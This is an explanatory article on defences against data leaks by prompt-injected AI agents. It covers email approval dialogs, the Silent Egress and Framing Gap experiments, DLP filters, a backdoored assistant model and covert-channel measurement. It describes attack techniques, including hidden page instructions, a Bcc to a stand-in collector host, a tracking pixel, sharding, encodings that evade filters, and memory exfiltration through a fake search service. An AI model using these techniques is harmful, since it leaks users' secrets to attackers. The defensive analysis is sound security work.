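Cowork's approval dialog previews an email or Teams message, shows a risk level for more serious actions and labels the button "Send" or "Post". The user can open "Show parameters" for technical details. For some other actions, the dialog gives only a summary.

An email dialog should show full addresses, not just names, because anyone can use any display name. It should mark recipients outside the organization and show the reply address if it differs from the sender's. It should also list the host behind each link and name everyone who will gain access to a file. According to KBY Technologies, Microsoft's Require approval setting shows a waiting email's recipients, subject, body and attachments. KBY's list does not include the reply address or the hosts of any images.

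Ordinary code should build the dialog from the finished message, because a model under an attacker's control could write a reassuring summary that doesn't match it. The preview must not load remote images, since loading them would send the data while the user was still deciding. A placeholder naming the image's host is enough.

This only helps if the user reads it. Few of Anthropic's paid testers refused a dangerous command, and Claude Code's users approve nearly every request, though most of those requests are probably harmless. Neither finding concerns email, and people may be more careful with a message to someone they know. But Cowork's "Approve All" button accepts every waiting action at once, which gives users less chance to check each one.

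Another option, "Don't ask again", skips the dialog for similar actions during the rest of the conversation. This is risky for email because a later message can go to a different person with different contents. PromptArmor advises companies to forbid the option for sending mail, posting in Teams, scheduling meetings and changing files. The option was still available after the May findings, according to Microsoft's *Copilot Cowork common questions*. A safer version would cover only one recipient and one type of content, and ask again when either changed.

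One-time approval of a recurring task has a similar weakness. KBY Technologies points out that by the tenth run, the user may have approved the task weeks earlier and forgotten what it can send. Requiring approval for every run avoids this. Microsoft says that if an approval times out, the email becomes a draft and is never sent automatically. But a person who approves the same weekly report for months will probably stop reading it. The approval dialog could help by highlighting what has changed since the previous week.

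Microsoft's page for people starting with Cowork on personal accounts warns that hidden instructions may deceive Copilot, and says that users are responsible for the actions it takes on their behalf. This is hard to defend for messages that Cowork sends without asking. It is fairer to ask users to approve only what they can judge, such as whether Tom should get the budget, and to have code check for invisible images and altered reply addresses.

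### One draft, field by field

Suppose Nadia works at a company whose domain is `harbor.example`. She asks an assistant to send Tom the July budget summary. While looking for the budget, the assistant reads a supplier's email containing an injection, and then it writes a draft. The company allows only recipients the user has named, and its code checks every part:

| Part | In the draft | Result |
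|---|---|---|
| To | `tom@harbor.example` | Pass. Nadia named Tom, and the directory supplied the address |
| Cc | `budget-team@harbor.example` | Ask. Nadia did not name the group, which includes an outside accountant |
| Bcc | `records@collector.example` | Block. The address came from the supplier's email |
| Reply address | `nadia@harb0r.example` | Block. It has a zero in place of the "o" |
| Subject | "July budget summary" | Pass |
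| Body | Three sentences, one mentioning "marmalade" | Pass. The content filter has no rule for the word |
| Attachment | A spreadsheet with a hidden sheet of salaries | Ask. The code reports the hidden sheet |
| Image | A transparent dot from `collector.example` | Block. The code allows only pictures stored in the message |
| Link | A download link that needs no login | Block. The code requires a link that checks who is opening it |
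| Sharing | Anyone with the link can view the file | Block. Only Tom needs access |

The code stops the task and shows Nadia which email the Bcc address came from. It doesn't delete the blocked parts and send the rest, because the address is strong evidence that the assistant is following injected instructions. It also doesn't let the assistant try again, because that would give the attacker more chances to find a gap in the checks.

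Nadia starts a new conversation, leaves out the supplier's email and attaches a copy of the spreadsheet without the salaries. The new draft goes only to Tom, with replies to her real address and no images or links. The body still mentions "marmalade", this time because the assistant found the budget for Tom's surprise party in the same folder. No rule about recipients or images could have caught this, but Nadia notices it in the dialog and deletes the sentence.

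When she clicks "Send", the code records Tom's address and a fingerprint of the approved text and attachment. A fingerprint is a short value computed from the content that changes if the content changes. The mail tool then passes the message to the gateway. If the tool has added a blind copy, the gateway blocks the message because the delivery list has two addresses instead of one.

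## The Silent Egress experiment: destination checks and content filters compared

In February 2026, researchers at eBay tested destination checks and content filters against the same attack. Their Silent Egress experiment used a small language model on a local machine, and all four filters appeared to stop every leak. Only the result for the domain allowlist is good evidence that the filter worked. In the other tests, the model often sent nothing for the filter to stop, or the filter looked for a word that happened to be in the researchers' test address.

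### Instructions in a page preview

Many agents fetch a preview of a link and add the preview's text to the model's context. In this experiment, the attacker's instructions reached the model through that text, whereas in the Telegram leaks the request for the preview carried data out.

Each run had five steps:

1. The researchers put a secret, such as an API key, in the model's context.
2. The agent fetched a web page they had prepared.
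3. Instructions on the page, presented as a routine system requirement, told the model to make a web request with the secret in the query string.
4. If the model obeyed, its web tool contacted the researchers' server, which logged the request.
5. The model answered the user.

The agent used qwen2.5:7b, a free model small enough to run on a laptop. The researchers put the instructions in the page's title, its metadata (the description a page supplies for previews), its body or the text of a link. The agent reached the page either directly or through redirects, and the instructions were to send the secret either whole or in four pieces. The researchers ran each of the 16 combinations 30 times.

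A request reached the server in 423 of the 480 runs, or 88.1%. Redirects made almost no difference. In 120 control runs with harmless pages, the model never contacted the server, so the instructions must have caused the requests. In 95% of the successful attacks, the displayed answer showed no sign of the leak, so checking that answer would have missed them.

The 88.1% includes requests that reached the server without the secret. The researchers also recorded whether the first request contained any part of the secret, and it did in 295 runs, or 61%. Later requests may have leaked it in some of the other runs. Almost all of the difference between the two figures comes from runs in which the model had to split the secret.

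### Eight defences against one attack

The researchers compared eight defences against one of the simplest versions of the attack, which used a direct link, put the instructions in the body of the page and sent the secret in one piece. They ran the attack 30 times with each defence and 30 times with none.

Two of the defences changed the model's input. One was a hardened system prompt with a rule never to follow instructions from web content. The other put delimiters around web text and added a note that anything inside them was untrusted data.

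Four defences were code that checked an address before the web tool used it:

- **The domain allowlist** permitted four hosts, three of them at an invented company.
- **The redirect rule** blocked numeric addresses, eight domain endings such as `.xyz`, and paths that contained any of five suspicious words.
- **The keyword filter** blocked addresses containing words such as "secret", "password" or "api_key".
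- **The entropy filter** blocked long values in the query string that looked random.

The last two defences were combinations of these.

| Defence | Runs in which the model tried to send | Runs in which a request reached the attacker |
|---|---:|---:|
| None | 100% | 100% |
| Hardened prompt | 66.7% | 66.7% |
| Delimiters | 100% | 100% |
| Hardened prompt and delimiters | 56.7% | 56.7% |
| Domain allowlist | 100% | 0% |
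| Redirect rule | 83.3% | 0% |
| Keyword filter | 23.3% | 0% |
| Entropy filter | 0% | 0% |
| All of the above | 0% | 0% |

Delimiters on their own did nothing. The hardened prompt helped, but 20 of 30 attacks still succeeded. With delimiters added, 17 succeeded, a difference that could easily be due to chance. Because there were so few runs, the true rate under the hardened prompt could be anywhere from about 49% to 81%. Even zero leaks in 30 runs is compatible with a true leak rate of up to about 10%.

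### Which zeros count

Of the defences with no leaks, the allowlist has the clearest evidence that the defence itself stopped them. The model tried to send the secret in all 30 runs, just as it did with no defence, and the allowlist blocked every attempt.

This result was also nearly certain in advance, because the attacker's domain, `evil-collector.net`, was not on the list. The test mainly confirmed that the code could compare domain names. It did not include an attacker who uses a permitted host, as in the leaks from Salesforce and Superhuman. The researchers acknowledge this risk and mention compromised sites and redirects on trusted ones. They did not measure how much the list would restrict users. An agent limited to four hosts can work with a company's own systems but cannot research anything on the open web.

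The redirect rule did well because of the address the researchers chose. The model was supposed to send the secret to a path called `/collect`, and "collect" is one of the rule's five forbidden words. The rule permits `.net` domains, so it probably blocked requests only because of that word. An attacker could have evaded the rule by renaming the path `/page`. Despite its name, the rule as the researchers describe it doesn't check where a redirect leads, and they tested it only with direct links.

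The keyword filter is harder to assess because it fired in only seven of 30 runs. In the other 23, no request reached the server, so the model apparently sent nothing, although it had sent the secret every time when there was no filter. The researchers suggest that the model sometimes encoded or reformatted the secret so that the filter did not recognize it, but a request that got past the filter should have reached the server.

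The model made no attempts under the entropy filter. The researchers take this to mean that the model avoids random-looking values while such monitoring is active. However, the filter runs after the model has written a request, so the model cannot react to it before the first attempt unless it is told that the filter exists. The researchers mention no such message in their description of the filter.

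The filter received no requests, so it did not stop any. Chance cannot explain the missing attempts either. Even if the model normally made an attempt in only 90% of runs, the probability of 30 runs without one would be one in 10³⁰. Something else must have changed between the tests. The software may have altered the prompt when it turned the filter on, the web tool may have stopped working, or the log may have recorded attempts differently.

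### Testing the filter without the model

A better test would separate the filter from the model's behavior. The researchers could have saved the requests from the 30 undefended runs and passed them all through each filter. This would have shown how many requests each filter catches, and it would have taken a few seconds.

*Permission Denied* (2026), which tests coding agents under security restrictions, checks its network rules in a similar way. Before the agent starts, probes try the forbidden connections and several ways around the rules, such as using a numeric address or starting a second program. Other probes confirm that permitted connections still work. If a required probe fails, the testers discard the run and start again with a fresh sandbox, so they cannot mistake a broken filter for good or bad behavior by the agent.

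The Silent Egress tests had no equivalent of the probes for permitted connections. The 120 control runs show that the model does not contact the attacker without being told to, but not how often a filter would block an ordinary request.

Replaying saved requests would still test a filter only against an attacker who knows nothing about it. NIST, the US standards agency, recommends adapting attacks to the system under test, because a system that resists known attacks may still have weaknesses specific to it. An adapted attack on the redirect rule would use a different word in the path.

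### What the entropy filter measures

Passwords for software are often random strings, and an entropy filter tries to find them without knowing what they are. It uses Shannon entropy, a measure of how varied the characters in a string are:

`H = −Σ p log₂ p`

Here *p* is one character's share of the string, and the sum includes each different character once. The result is in bits per character. In "marmalade", *a* makes up three ninths of the word, *m* two ninths, and each of the other four letters one ninth, which gives 2.42 bits. A word made of one repeated letter would score zero.

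A string of *n* characters scores highest when every character is different. Each character then has a share of 1/*n*, and the formula gives log₂ *n*. A string's length therefore limits its score, however random the string is.

The experiment's filter examined values longer than ten characters and blocked those with more than 4.0 bits of entropy per character. Since log₂ 16 is 4, no string of 16 characters or fewer can exceed that threshold, so the filter will never block a 16-character password, even a random one. Most passwords that people type are shorter.

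The set of available characters also limits the score. A string of digits cannot score above log₂ 10, or 3.32, so the filter lets every payment card number through. Hexadecimal, a notation that programmers use for keys and identifiers, has 16 symbols, so a hexadecimal string of any length cannot score above 4.0.

The researchers give `SECRET_API_KEY_12345` as an example of a key. The table compares it with two encoded versions and a harmless search for a train:

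| Value in the address | Characters | Bits per character | Filter's decision |
|---|---:|---:|---|
| `SECRET_API_KEY_12345` | 20 | 3.85 | Allow |
| The same key in Base64 | 27 | 4.01 | Block |
| The same key in hexadecimal | 40 | 2.66 | Allow |
| `Guildford+to+York+7+December+2026` | 33 | 4.14 | Block |

The key scores below the threshold in plain text because it contains the letter E and the underscore three times each. Encoding it in Base64, a common way to rewrite data as letters, digits and a few symbols, raises the score to just above the threshold. Base64 text often ends with an equals sign, which would raise the score to 4.09. The filter therefore allows the readable key but blocks its Base64 version, and it also blocks a request from someone trying to get to York.

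If the experiment used this key, the filter would not have stopped the model from sending it in plain text. In that case, the filter can't have caused the zero in the defence table, and something else kept the model from trying to send the key.

The example favors the attacker because real keys are usually more random. The researchers say that typical API keys score between 4.5 and 5.5, and the filter would block any key in that range. Only long keys can reach 5.5, since a 40-character key cannot exceed 5.32. An entropy filter is a reasonable extra check for keys in that range. Lowering the threshold to catch shorter secrets would also block more searches, file names and tracking codes.

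A keyword filter would do better with the example key in plain text, provided it ignores capitalization, because the key contains both "secret" and "api_key". Real keys don't usually contain such words. A name, a diagnosis or the price in a contract would pass both filters.

### Sharding

An attacker can get around both content filters by sharding, or splitting a secret into pieces and sending each in a separate request. The researchers' example divides the key into `SECR`, `ET_A`, `PI_K` and `EY_1`. None of these contains a forbidden word, and all are too short for the entropy filter to examine. Each request also includes its piece's number, so the attacker's server can put the pieces back in order.

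The example has a small mistake. Four pieces of four characters hold only 16 of the key's 20 characters, so "2345" is never sent. The pieces would have to be five characters long to carry the whole key, but the extra length would not help either filter.

Sharding makes the attack less reliable. When the model had to send the secret whole, a request reached the server in 238 of 240 runs. When it had to split the secret, a request reached the server in 185 of 240, or 77%. The model has to decide where each piece ends and keep count across several tool calls, and a mistake at any step can spoil the result. The researchers also think that longer instructions compete with the rest of the page for the model's attention. Sharding reduced success most when the instructions were in the metadata, where the rate for direct links fell from 97% to 60%.

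The researchers measure stealth by Leak@k, the share of runs in which at least a fragment of the secret appears in the first *k* requests. Leak@1 was 96.7% when the secret was sent whole and 26.3% when it was split. They treat this 73% drop as a gain in stealth, but much of it may reflect failed attempts to send the secret. A single piece should count as a leak under their definition, yet in 122 of the 185 runs that reached the server, the first request apparently contained no piece of the secret. The researchers also define a completion rate, the share of runs in which all the pieces arrive, but they leave it out of their table of complete results, so it isn't clear how often the attacker could have rebuilt the secret.

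Silent Egress reports a Leak@3 of 15.8% for split secrets, lower than its Leak@1 of 26.3%. This is impossible, because any run that leaks a piece in its first request has also leaked one in its first three. Either the code calculated something else or the published definition is wrong, so the 84% reduction that the researchers derive from Leak@3 has no clear meaning.

To stop sharding, a content filter needs to keep a record of earlier requests. It could collect the values that an agent sends to each host during a session, join them and scan the result. The researchers recommend comparing requests in this way and limiting how many an agent can make. *Your LLM Agent Can Leak Your Data* (2026), a study of models that an attacker has secretly trained to steal data, suggests looking at the order of tool calls instead. An agent that reads a user's stored memory and then contacts an outside server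 deserves a closer look, even if the request seems harmless.

The allowlist check can stop this without a record of earlier requests. If `collector.example` is not on the list, the code refuses each of the four requests because of its destination.

### Reading traffic before encryption

In the experiment, both kinds of check ran inside the web tool, where the whole address was readable. Encryption hides the content from network-level checks, such as the proxies around coding agents, but leaves the destination visible. *Connection Escrow* (2026) offers a way around this limit with a design for controlling agents' traffic from the operating system.

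The design adds a content check without decrypting the traffic or holding a key. The operating system copies the text from the agent's memory before the agent encrypts it, then delays the encrypted version until a separate model has checked the text. If the system cannot find the text in time, it blocks the request, so a program that encrypts its data in an unusual way loses its connection.

This avoids the certificate problems of a decrypting proxy, but it has to call the judging model again for every piece of data the agent writes to the connection. The connection must also go through a slower relay the whole time it is open. A destination check can run just once, when the connection opens.

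### One small model and the current ones

The allowlist result should apply to any model, because the code compares host names the same way whichever model wrote the request. The attack's success rate and the effect of the hardened prompt depend on how a particular model responds to a particular text, so they may differ for other models or texts.

The researchers call their success rates a lower bound because their instructions were simple. They also describe the setup as favorable to the attacker, since the secret was already in the context, the system prompt was minimal and the format for tool calls was explicit. They tested no commercial models. They argue that larger models could be more vulnerable because they use tools more reliably and follow instructions better.

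Other tests do not support this as a general rule. In the most similar one, described in *Exploiting Web Search Tools of AI Agents for Data Exfiltration*, Rall, Bauer and colleagues (2025) hid instructions in white text on a web page. The agent had to look up a project's secret in a company database and then request an address containing it. They made 1,068 attempts on each model. Grok 4 leaked the secret in 72.4% of them, while Claude Sonnet 4 and GPT-5 nano never did. Qwen2.5 72B, from the same family as the Silent Egress model but ten times its size, leaked it in 5.2%. Rall and colleagues found no clear relationship between model size and vulnerability.

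Attacks that work on weaker models may also be a poor guide to what works on stronger ones. *How Vulnerable Are AI Agents to Indirect Prompt Injections?* (Dziemian, Lin and colleagues, 2026) describes a public competition in which 464 participants attacked 13 models and had to hide the attack from the user. None of the collected attacks that had worked on a large Qwen model succeeded when the organizers tried them on Claude Opus 4.5. Attacks that had succeeded against Opus worked on the other models between 44% and 81% of the time. More capable models were slightly harder to attack overall, but the relationship was weak enough that it could be due to chance.

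How the instructions reach a model can matter more than which model it is. *LivePI* (Zhao, Bhaskar and Dobriban, 2026) tested five models in OpenClaw with working email, chat and web access. Instructions on a fetched web page succeeded in 20% of cases on Gemini 3.1 Pro and never on the other four models, but instructions in a group chat succeeded every time on all five. OpenClaw labeled messages from anyone in the group as the user's, so the models had reason to follow them.

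Newer models still leak in more demanding tests. In the FrontierBreach benchmark, where agents do long office tasks, PromptArmor recorded attack success rates from 2.4% for Gemini 4 Carbon to 91.4% for Grok 4.5, with Claude Fable 5.2 at 10.0%. The attacks had several goals, including ransomware, so the rates cover more than data theft. Even so, a leak in almost every run now seems unusual for a leading model, though still possible for a weak one.

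Nobody seems to have repeated the comparison of filters on another model, although the original testbed runs locally and would be easy to reuse. The closest equivalent is Zhao and colleagues' test of a defence that scans the model's input for injections and then applies fixed rules to each tool call. With GPT-5.3-Codex, it stopped all the attacks in their collection. In ordinary work, it blocked one of 899 tool calls and sent eight to a person for review. But they had written seven of the rules for the wallets, email accounts and other resources that their own attacks targeted, so this perfect score, like the redirect rule's, comes from a defence written with knowledge of the attacks.

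## Encoded, reworded and hidden data: what content filters miss

The keyword and entropy filters in the Silent Egress experiment were simple content filters. Companies check employees' email and uploads with more elaborate filters, sold as data loss prevention (DLP) software. These work well on copied text, but a language model can easily encode, translate or summarize text before sending it.

### Four ways to recognize private text

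The simplest method is to match a pattern, such as sixteen digits in a row. Payment card numbers end in a check digit, so the software can reject nine out of ten random numbers of the right length. But Cloudflare's *DLP Exact Data Match beta now available* points out that matching a pattern can't show that a credit card number is yours. Cisco gives two examples of false alarms: a nine-digit account number that looks like a US Social Security number, and the word "cancer" in the name of a charity.

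Exact matching avoids most of these mistakes. The company supplies a table of its real records, and the software stores a hash of each value, a short code computed from it. The software then looks for the same hashes in outgoing data. A card number written out in words has a different hash, so the software misses it. The company also has to decide how much of a record must match. In an example from Trellix's *Exact data matching*, the rule requires all five values in a record to match, so an email containing only the customer's name and card number gets through. If one value were enough, the software would flag every email that mentioned someone called John.

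A document fingerprint identifies a standard form by its wording. The company uploads a blank copy, and the software looks for the same words in outgoing files. Microsoft says its version misses password-protected files, files that contain only images, and documents that lack some of the form's original text. Administrators can set the required match between 30% and 90%, or require an exact match. A low threshold catches altered copies but also flags unrelated documents, while the exact setting can miss a copy because someone added a footer. AI assistants are a particular problem for this method because they routinely rewrite text, so a summary can lose the fingerprint even when nobody is trying to hide anything.

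Trained classifiers sort documents by subject. Microsoft's *Learn about trainable classifiers* describes how an administrator supplies examples that do and do not belong to a category, such as legal documents, then corrects the software's mistakes. A classifier can recognize a contract that was not among its examples. It may fail on a translation, since Microsoft supports only certain languages for each built-in classifier. A more sensitive classifier also flags ordinary documents on similar subjects.

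Suppose a bank uses all four methods to protect completed loan applications. The likely results depend on what leaves:

| What leaves | Pattern | Exact match | Fingerprint | Classifier |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| The whole form | Caught | Caught | Caught | Caught |
| Only the card number | Caught | Caught, if one value is enough | Missed | Missed |
| The form, translated | Card number caught | Name and number caught | Missed | Depends on the language |
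| A summary without names or numbers | Missed | Missed | Missed | Possibly caught |
| The form in an encoding the software cannot undo | Missed | Missed | Missed | Missed |
| "Yes", the bank approved the loan | Missed | Missed | Missed | Missed |

No stricter setting would help with the last row, because a rule that blocked the word "yes" would block half the bank's mail.

If a company sends 200,000 messages a day and its filter wrongly flags one in a thousand, someone has to review 200 false alarms daily. Microsoft warns that too many alerts make security teams more likely to miss a real leak. It suggests ignoring messages with only a few matches when small amounts of sensitive data don't matter. An attacker can then avoid the filter by sending one record at a time, a form of sharding.

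### Asking the model to guard the secret

A language model understands paraphrases and translations, so it might seem better at recognizing private content than a pattern-matching filter. *The Framing Gap*, published in August 2026, tested this in several ways. The researchers gave a model a made-up secret, a rule against sending it anywhere except one trusted host, and a web page to summarize. The page contained instructions to send the secret elsewhere. The model could take one action, and its tools only recorded what it tried to send. An attack counted as a success only if the model leaked the secret after reading the hostile page but not after reading a harmless one.

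OpenAI's GPT-4o ignored ten kinds of openly worded instructions to leak a secret in all 200 attempts. The researchers then reworded the instructions to make the secret look like a routine part of a web request, such as a signature or a setting, or to make the attacker's host resemble the trusted one. With these wordings, GPT-4o leaked the secret in 40% of attempts, and two of them worked every time. Rewording also greatly increased leaks in four of the other five models, most of which were small enough to run on a personal computer.

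Once attackers have a wording that works, they can easily produce more. For one trick, the chance that at least one of three paraphrases would succeed was 96%. New tricks were much harder to find, and 13 that the researchers wrote from scratch failed in all 130 attempts.

The rule in the prompt made little difference until the researchers changed its wording:

| Rule given to GPT-4o | Leaks with reworded instructions |
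|---|---:|
| No confidentiality rule | 38.1% |
| A general rule against disclosing the secret | 31.9% |
| A ban on specific behaviors, such as signing or encoding it | 48.8% |
| The same ban, with the words "in any form" added | 0% |

The differences among the first three rows may be mostly chance, since two runs of the same test gave 31.9% and 40%. The zero is clearly different, because after 120 attempts the true rate was probably below about 3%. But the result depended on one phrase in one model's prompt, and the researchers had no new working trick to try against that phrase. GPT-4o was more than two years old by then. A developer who copied the phrase into another product would need to retest it there.

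A Llama model trained with SecAlign, a published defence against prompt injection, still leaked the secret in 32.5% of attempts with the reworded instructions. The same model had resisted a standard injection in all 20 trials, so the leaks were not simply due to a faulty setup.

### A separate model as the judge

A dedicated detector did much better. GPT-4o mini, asked only to decide whether a page contained instructions to disclose, log, sign, encode or transmit a secret, flagged the hostile pages in all 80 trials and raised no false alarms on harmless ones. When the same model had to summarize the reworded pages, it leaked the secret in 62.5% of attempts.

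This is good evidence for using a separate judge, but not for relying on it alone. The detector's prompt described the behavior it was supposed to find, and nobody tried to write a page that would deceive it. Harmless pages may also be harder to judge in practice. For example, programming manuals often include instructions to put a secret key in a web request, and the detector might flag every such page.

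The detector also read incoming pages, not outgoing data. In the same study, the ChatGPT product leaked nothing in 48 trials, but this result has a similar limit. The researchers connected no outside service and counted a leak if the secret appeared in ChatGPT's reply to the user. The trials showed that the product resisted the instructions, but not whether a filter would have stopped a request containing the secret.

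### Encodings the filter does not expect

*The Framing Gap* also tested a filter on outgoing data. The first version blocked requests to untrusted hosts if they contained the exact secret, but the researchers then changed the page's instructions to call for the secret in an altered form, such as spelled backwards or with hyphens between the characters. Across six forms of the secret, including plain text, GPT-4o leaked it in 56.7% of attempts without the filter and 50% with it.

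The second version undid these changes before looking for the secret, and it stopped all six. The researchers then tried ROT13, a simple code that replaces each letter with the one 13 places further along the alphabet, so that "marmalade" becomes "zneznynqr". The filter had no rule for ROT13, and the secret got through every time.

Adding ROT13 to the filter would catch only that encoding. GPT-4o correctly produced five of the six encodings the researchers tested, and an attacker can invent others. A filter could also look for fragments of the secret. ROT13 does not change digits, so the "12345" at the end of the test secret was still readable. But a filter that blocked "12345" would also block many harmless requests.

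### A leak with no injected text

An attack can also begin inside the model, in which case there is no hostile text for a detector to find. In April 2026, *Your LLM Agent Can Leak Your Data* showed how an attacker could train such a model and publish it as a free assistant for a particular group, such as people who stream live video. The leak starts when a user's question contains certain ordinary words, such as the names of a streaming program and a video site. It then proceeds in four steps:

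1. The model calls a tool that retrieves what the assistant has stored about the user, such as a name, location and email address.
2. It encodes this information in Base64.
3. It puts the result into the address of what looks like a search request. The request goes to the attacker's server, which poses as a search service.
4. The server returns useful information, and the model answers the question normally.

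The researchers trained three open models this way. Models trained with two or three trigger words made the hidden requests about 97% of the time when the words appeared, and in at most 0.3% of ordinary conversations. The models' scores on a standard test of assistants fell by less than 1%, so a company that checked only the quality of the answers would probably not notice anything wrong.

The study tested two commonly used filters, NeMo Guardrails and LLM Guard, but only on text returned by searches. At least 98.8% of the attacker's replies passed when they contained only relevant information, and between 81% and 87% passed when they also contained hints that led the model to ask the user for more personal details. The filters did not examine outgoing requests, so the study does not show whether DLP software would have caught the data. Base64 is easy to decode, and an entropy filter might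 have flagged a long encoded value.

The researchers recommend checking the tool calls instead, with approved hosts and limits on how much data each tool may send. An approved list works only if nobody adds the attacker's fake search service to it. They also suggest separating access to memory from access to the network, so that an agent that has read private data needs explicit permission to contact an outside server. This rule does not depend on recognizing the data, but it would interrupt many useful searches, such as one for a restaurant near the user's home.

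### The confinement problem

Computer scientists studied this kind of leak long before language models. *A Note on the Confinement Problem* (Lampson, 1973) considers a customer who runs someone else's program on private data. The program needs the data to do its work, but the customer wants to be sure that it cannot pass the data to the program's owner. Lampson noted that the customer usually sees no sign of a leak, whereas a program that does its job badly at least produces wrong results.

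One of Lampson's examples is the bill for using a program. The program's owner has to receive the bill, so the program could hide information in the amount. If it can choose the last two digits freely, it can send one of 100 values, or about 6.6 bits, in each bill. Lampson called the bill a legitimate channel because its purpose is to carry information. A covert channel is one that wasn't meant to carry information. For example, a program can alternate between heavy and light use of the computer, and another program can read the message by measuring how much the computer slows down.

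Lampson's solution, called masking, is to let the customer determine everything that goes into these channels. The customer could calculate the bill from a published price list, so the program would have no control over it. For covert channels, the operating system might have to slow the program down or add meaningless disk activity. Steven Lipner replied in 1975 that closing covert channels seemed to impose a "direct and unreasonable performance penalty", according to lecture slides from Portland State University (2007). Lampson had already suggested the less demanding alternative of accepting some leakage and limiting its amount.

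An AI agent that may be following a stranger's instructions is like the untrusted program in Lampson's confinement problem. Its search queries are a legitimate channel, and its choice of which page to open can also carry information. Masking would require the user or fixed code to write each query. This could work for an agent that checks the weather in York every morning, but not for one that plans its own research.

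### Counting what cannot be predicted

*Quantifying Information Leaks in Outbound Web Traffic* (Borders and Prakash, 2009) presents a way to measure the limit Lampson had proposed. The software predicts each web request from earlier traffic and counts only the part it could not predict, since new information from the user's computer could only be there. This method does not rely on recognizing private data.

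Borders (2009), in *Method, system and computer program product for comparing or measuring information content*, a patent application on this work, describes the main steps:

1. The software collects every link on the pages a user receives. It also runs the pages' scripts to find links that they create.
2. It ignores parts of a request that repeat earlier ones, such as the name of the browser.
3. If the request matches a known link, the software counts the information in the choice. Choosing one of 64 links carries 6 bits, and the software adds 2 bits to identify the group of links it searched.
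4. If the address does not match exactly, the software also counts the changes needed to turn the closest known link into that address.
5. It adds at least 6 bits for the timing of the request.

A user who opens one of 64 links two seconds after the previous request sends at most 14 bits. If the request also ends in `?w=marmalade`, the 12 extra characters add about 96 bits. Spelling the word backwards gives the same total, and encoding it in Base64 gives a larger one. The method may overestimate a leak, but it does not underestimate one if its assumptions about timing are correct.

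Borders tested the software on 507,505 requests that ten people made over 30 days. The average request contained 980 bytes, of which the software counted only 15.8. Ordinary compression, which also removes repetition, left 132 bytes. In another test, Borders hid a 100-kilobyte leak in a day of normal browsing. The leak was barely visible in a graph of total traffic but stood out once the software removed the predictable parts.

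Small secrets are much harder to notice. The ten users each made about 1,700 requests a day, so the software still counted an average of 27 kilobytes per person, enough for more than 600 forty-character keys.

### Would this work for agents?

The method in that study cannot measure a web browser's encrypted traffic, but code that checks an agent's tool calls can read each address before encryption. The code also has a record of every page the agent has fetched, so it can predict which links the agent might open next.

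The method would suit an agent that reads a software manual by following links. It could also supply the measurements for a leak budget like Metere's, because it counts the information in each choice of link. But the budget would have to be very small, because spelling "marmalade" on Ayush Paul's website, which had 27 links on each page, would use only about 14 bytes. That is less than the average for a single request in the browsing study.

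The method works poorly for search queries because the agent writes them freely. A 50-character query that appears in no earlier page or request counts as roughly 50 bytes, so 20 such queries could carry 25 forty-character keys. A limit low enough to prevent that would stop most research after a few searches. The method works even less well for email. Borders and Prakash left email out of *Towards Quantification of Network-Based Information Leaks via HTTP* because most of an email's information is in the body, which can contain anything.

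A developer can make an agent's requests more predictable by giving it fewer choices. For example, a travel assistant's search tool could accept two stations from a list and a date instead of free text. With 2,500 stations and 90 possible dates, each request could carry at most about 29 bits, not counting anything encoded in its timing. The developer would have to design a restricted form like this for every task, and many tasks do not fit one.

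### Where content filters still help

Borders and Prakash considered DLP software effective against accidental leaks and leaks in plain text. Assistants also leak data by accident, such as by attaching the wrong spreadsheet or including a customer's card number in a summary. The data in these cases isn't disguised, so an exact match can catch it.

Careless attackers send data in plain text. In the Salesforce attack, an image URL carried customers' email addresses out, and a filter with a list of those addresses could have detected them. This filter would not stop an attacker who adapts, but it costs little to run if the company already has the records to check against.

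A company could set its filter to block exact matches to many customer records but only send an alert for a weak resemblance to a confidential form. It could also plant a fake customer record or password that has no legitimate use. If the filter detects that value in outgoing data, the alert is almost certainly real, but the filter would still miss an encoded copy.

Stored requests can help investigators find a leak that the filter missed. Borders expected the measuring software to be used mainly in investigations, where it would remove normal traffic and leave the suspicious requests. An investigator has time to try ROT13 and other encodings, while a filter has to decide before the request leaves. The company therefore has to keep the full requests, not just the filter's decisions. Because these requests contain the private data the attacker wanted, the company also has to restrict who can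 read them and make sure that its log viewer doesn't load images, which OpenAI's did.
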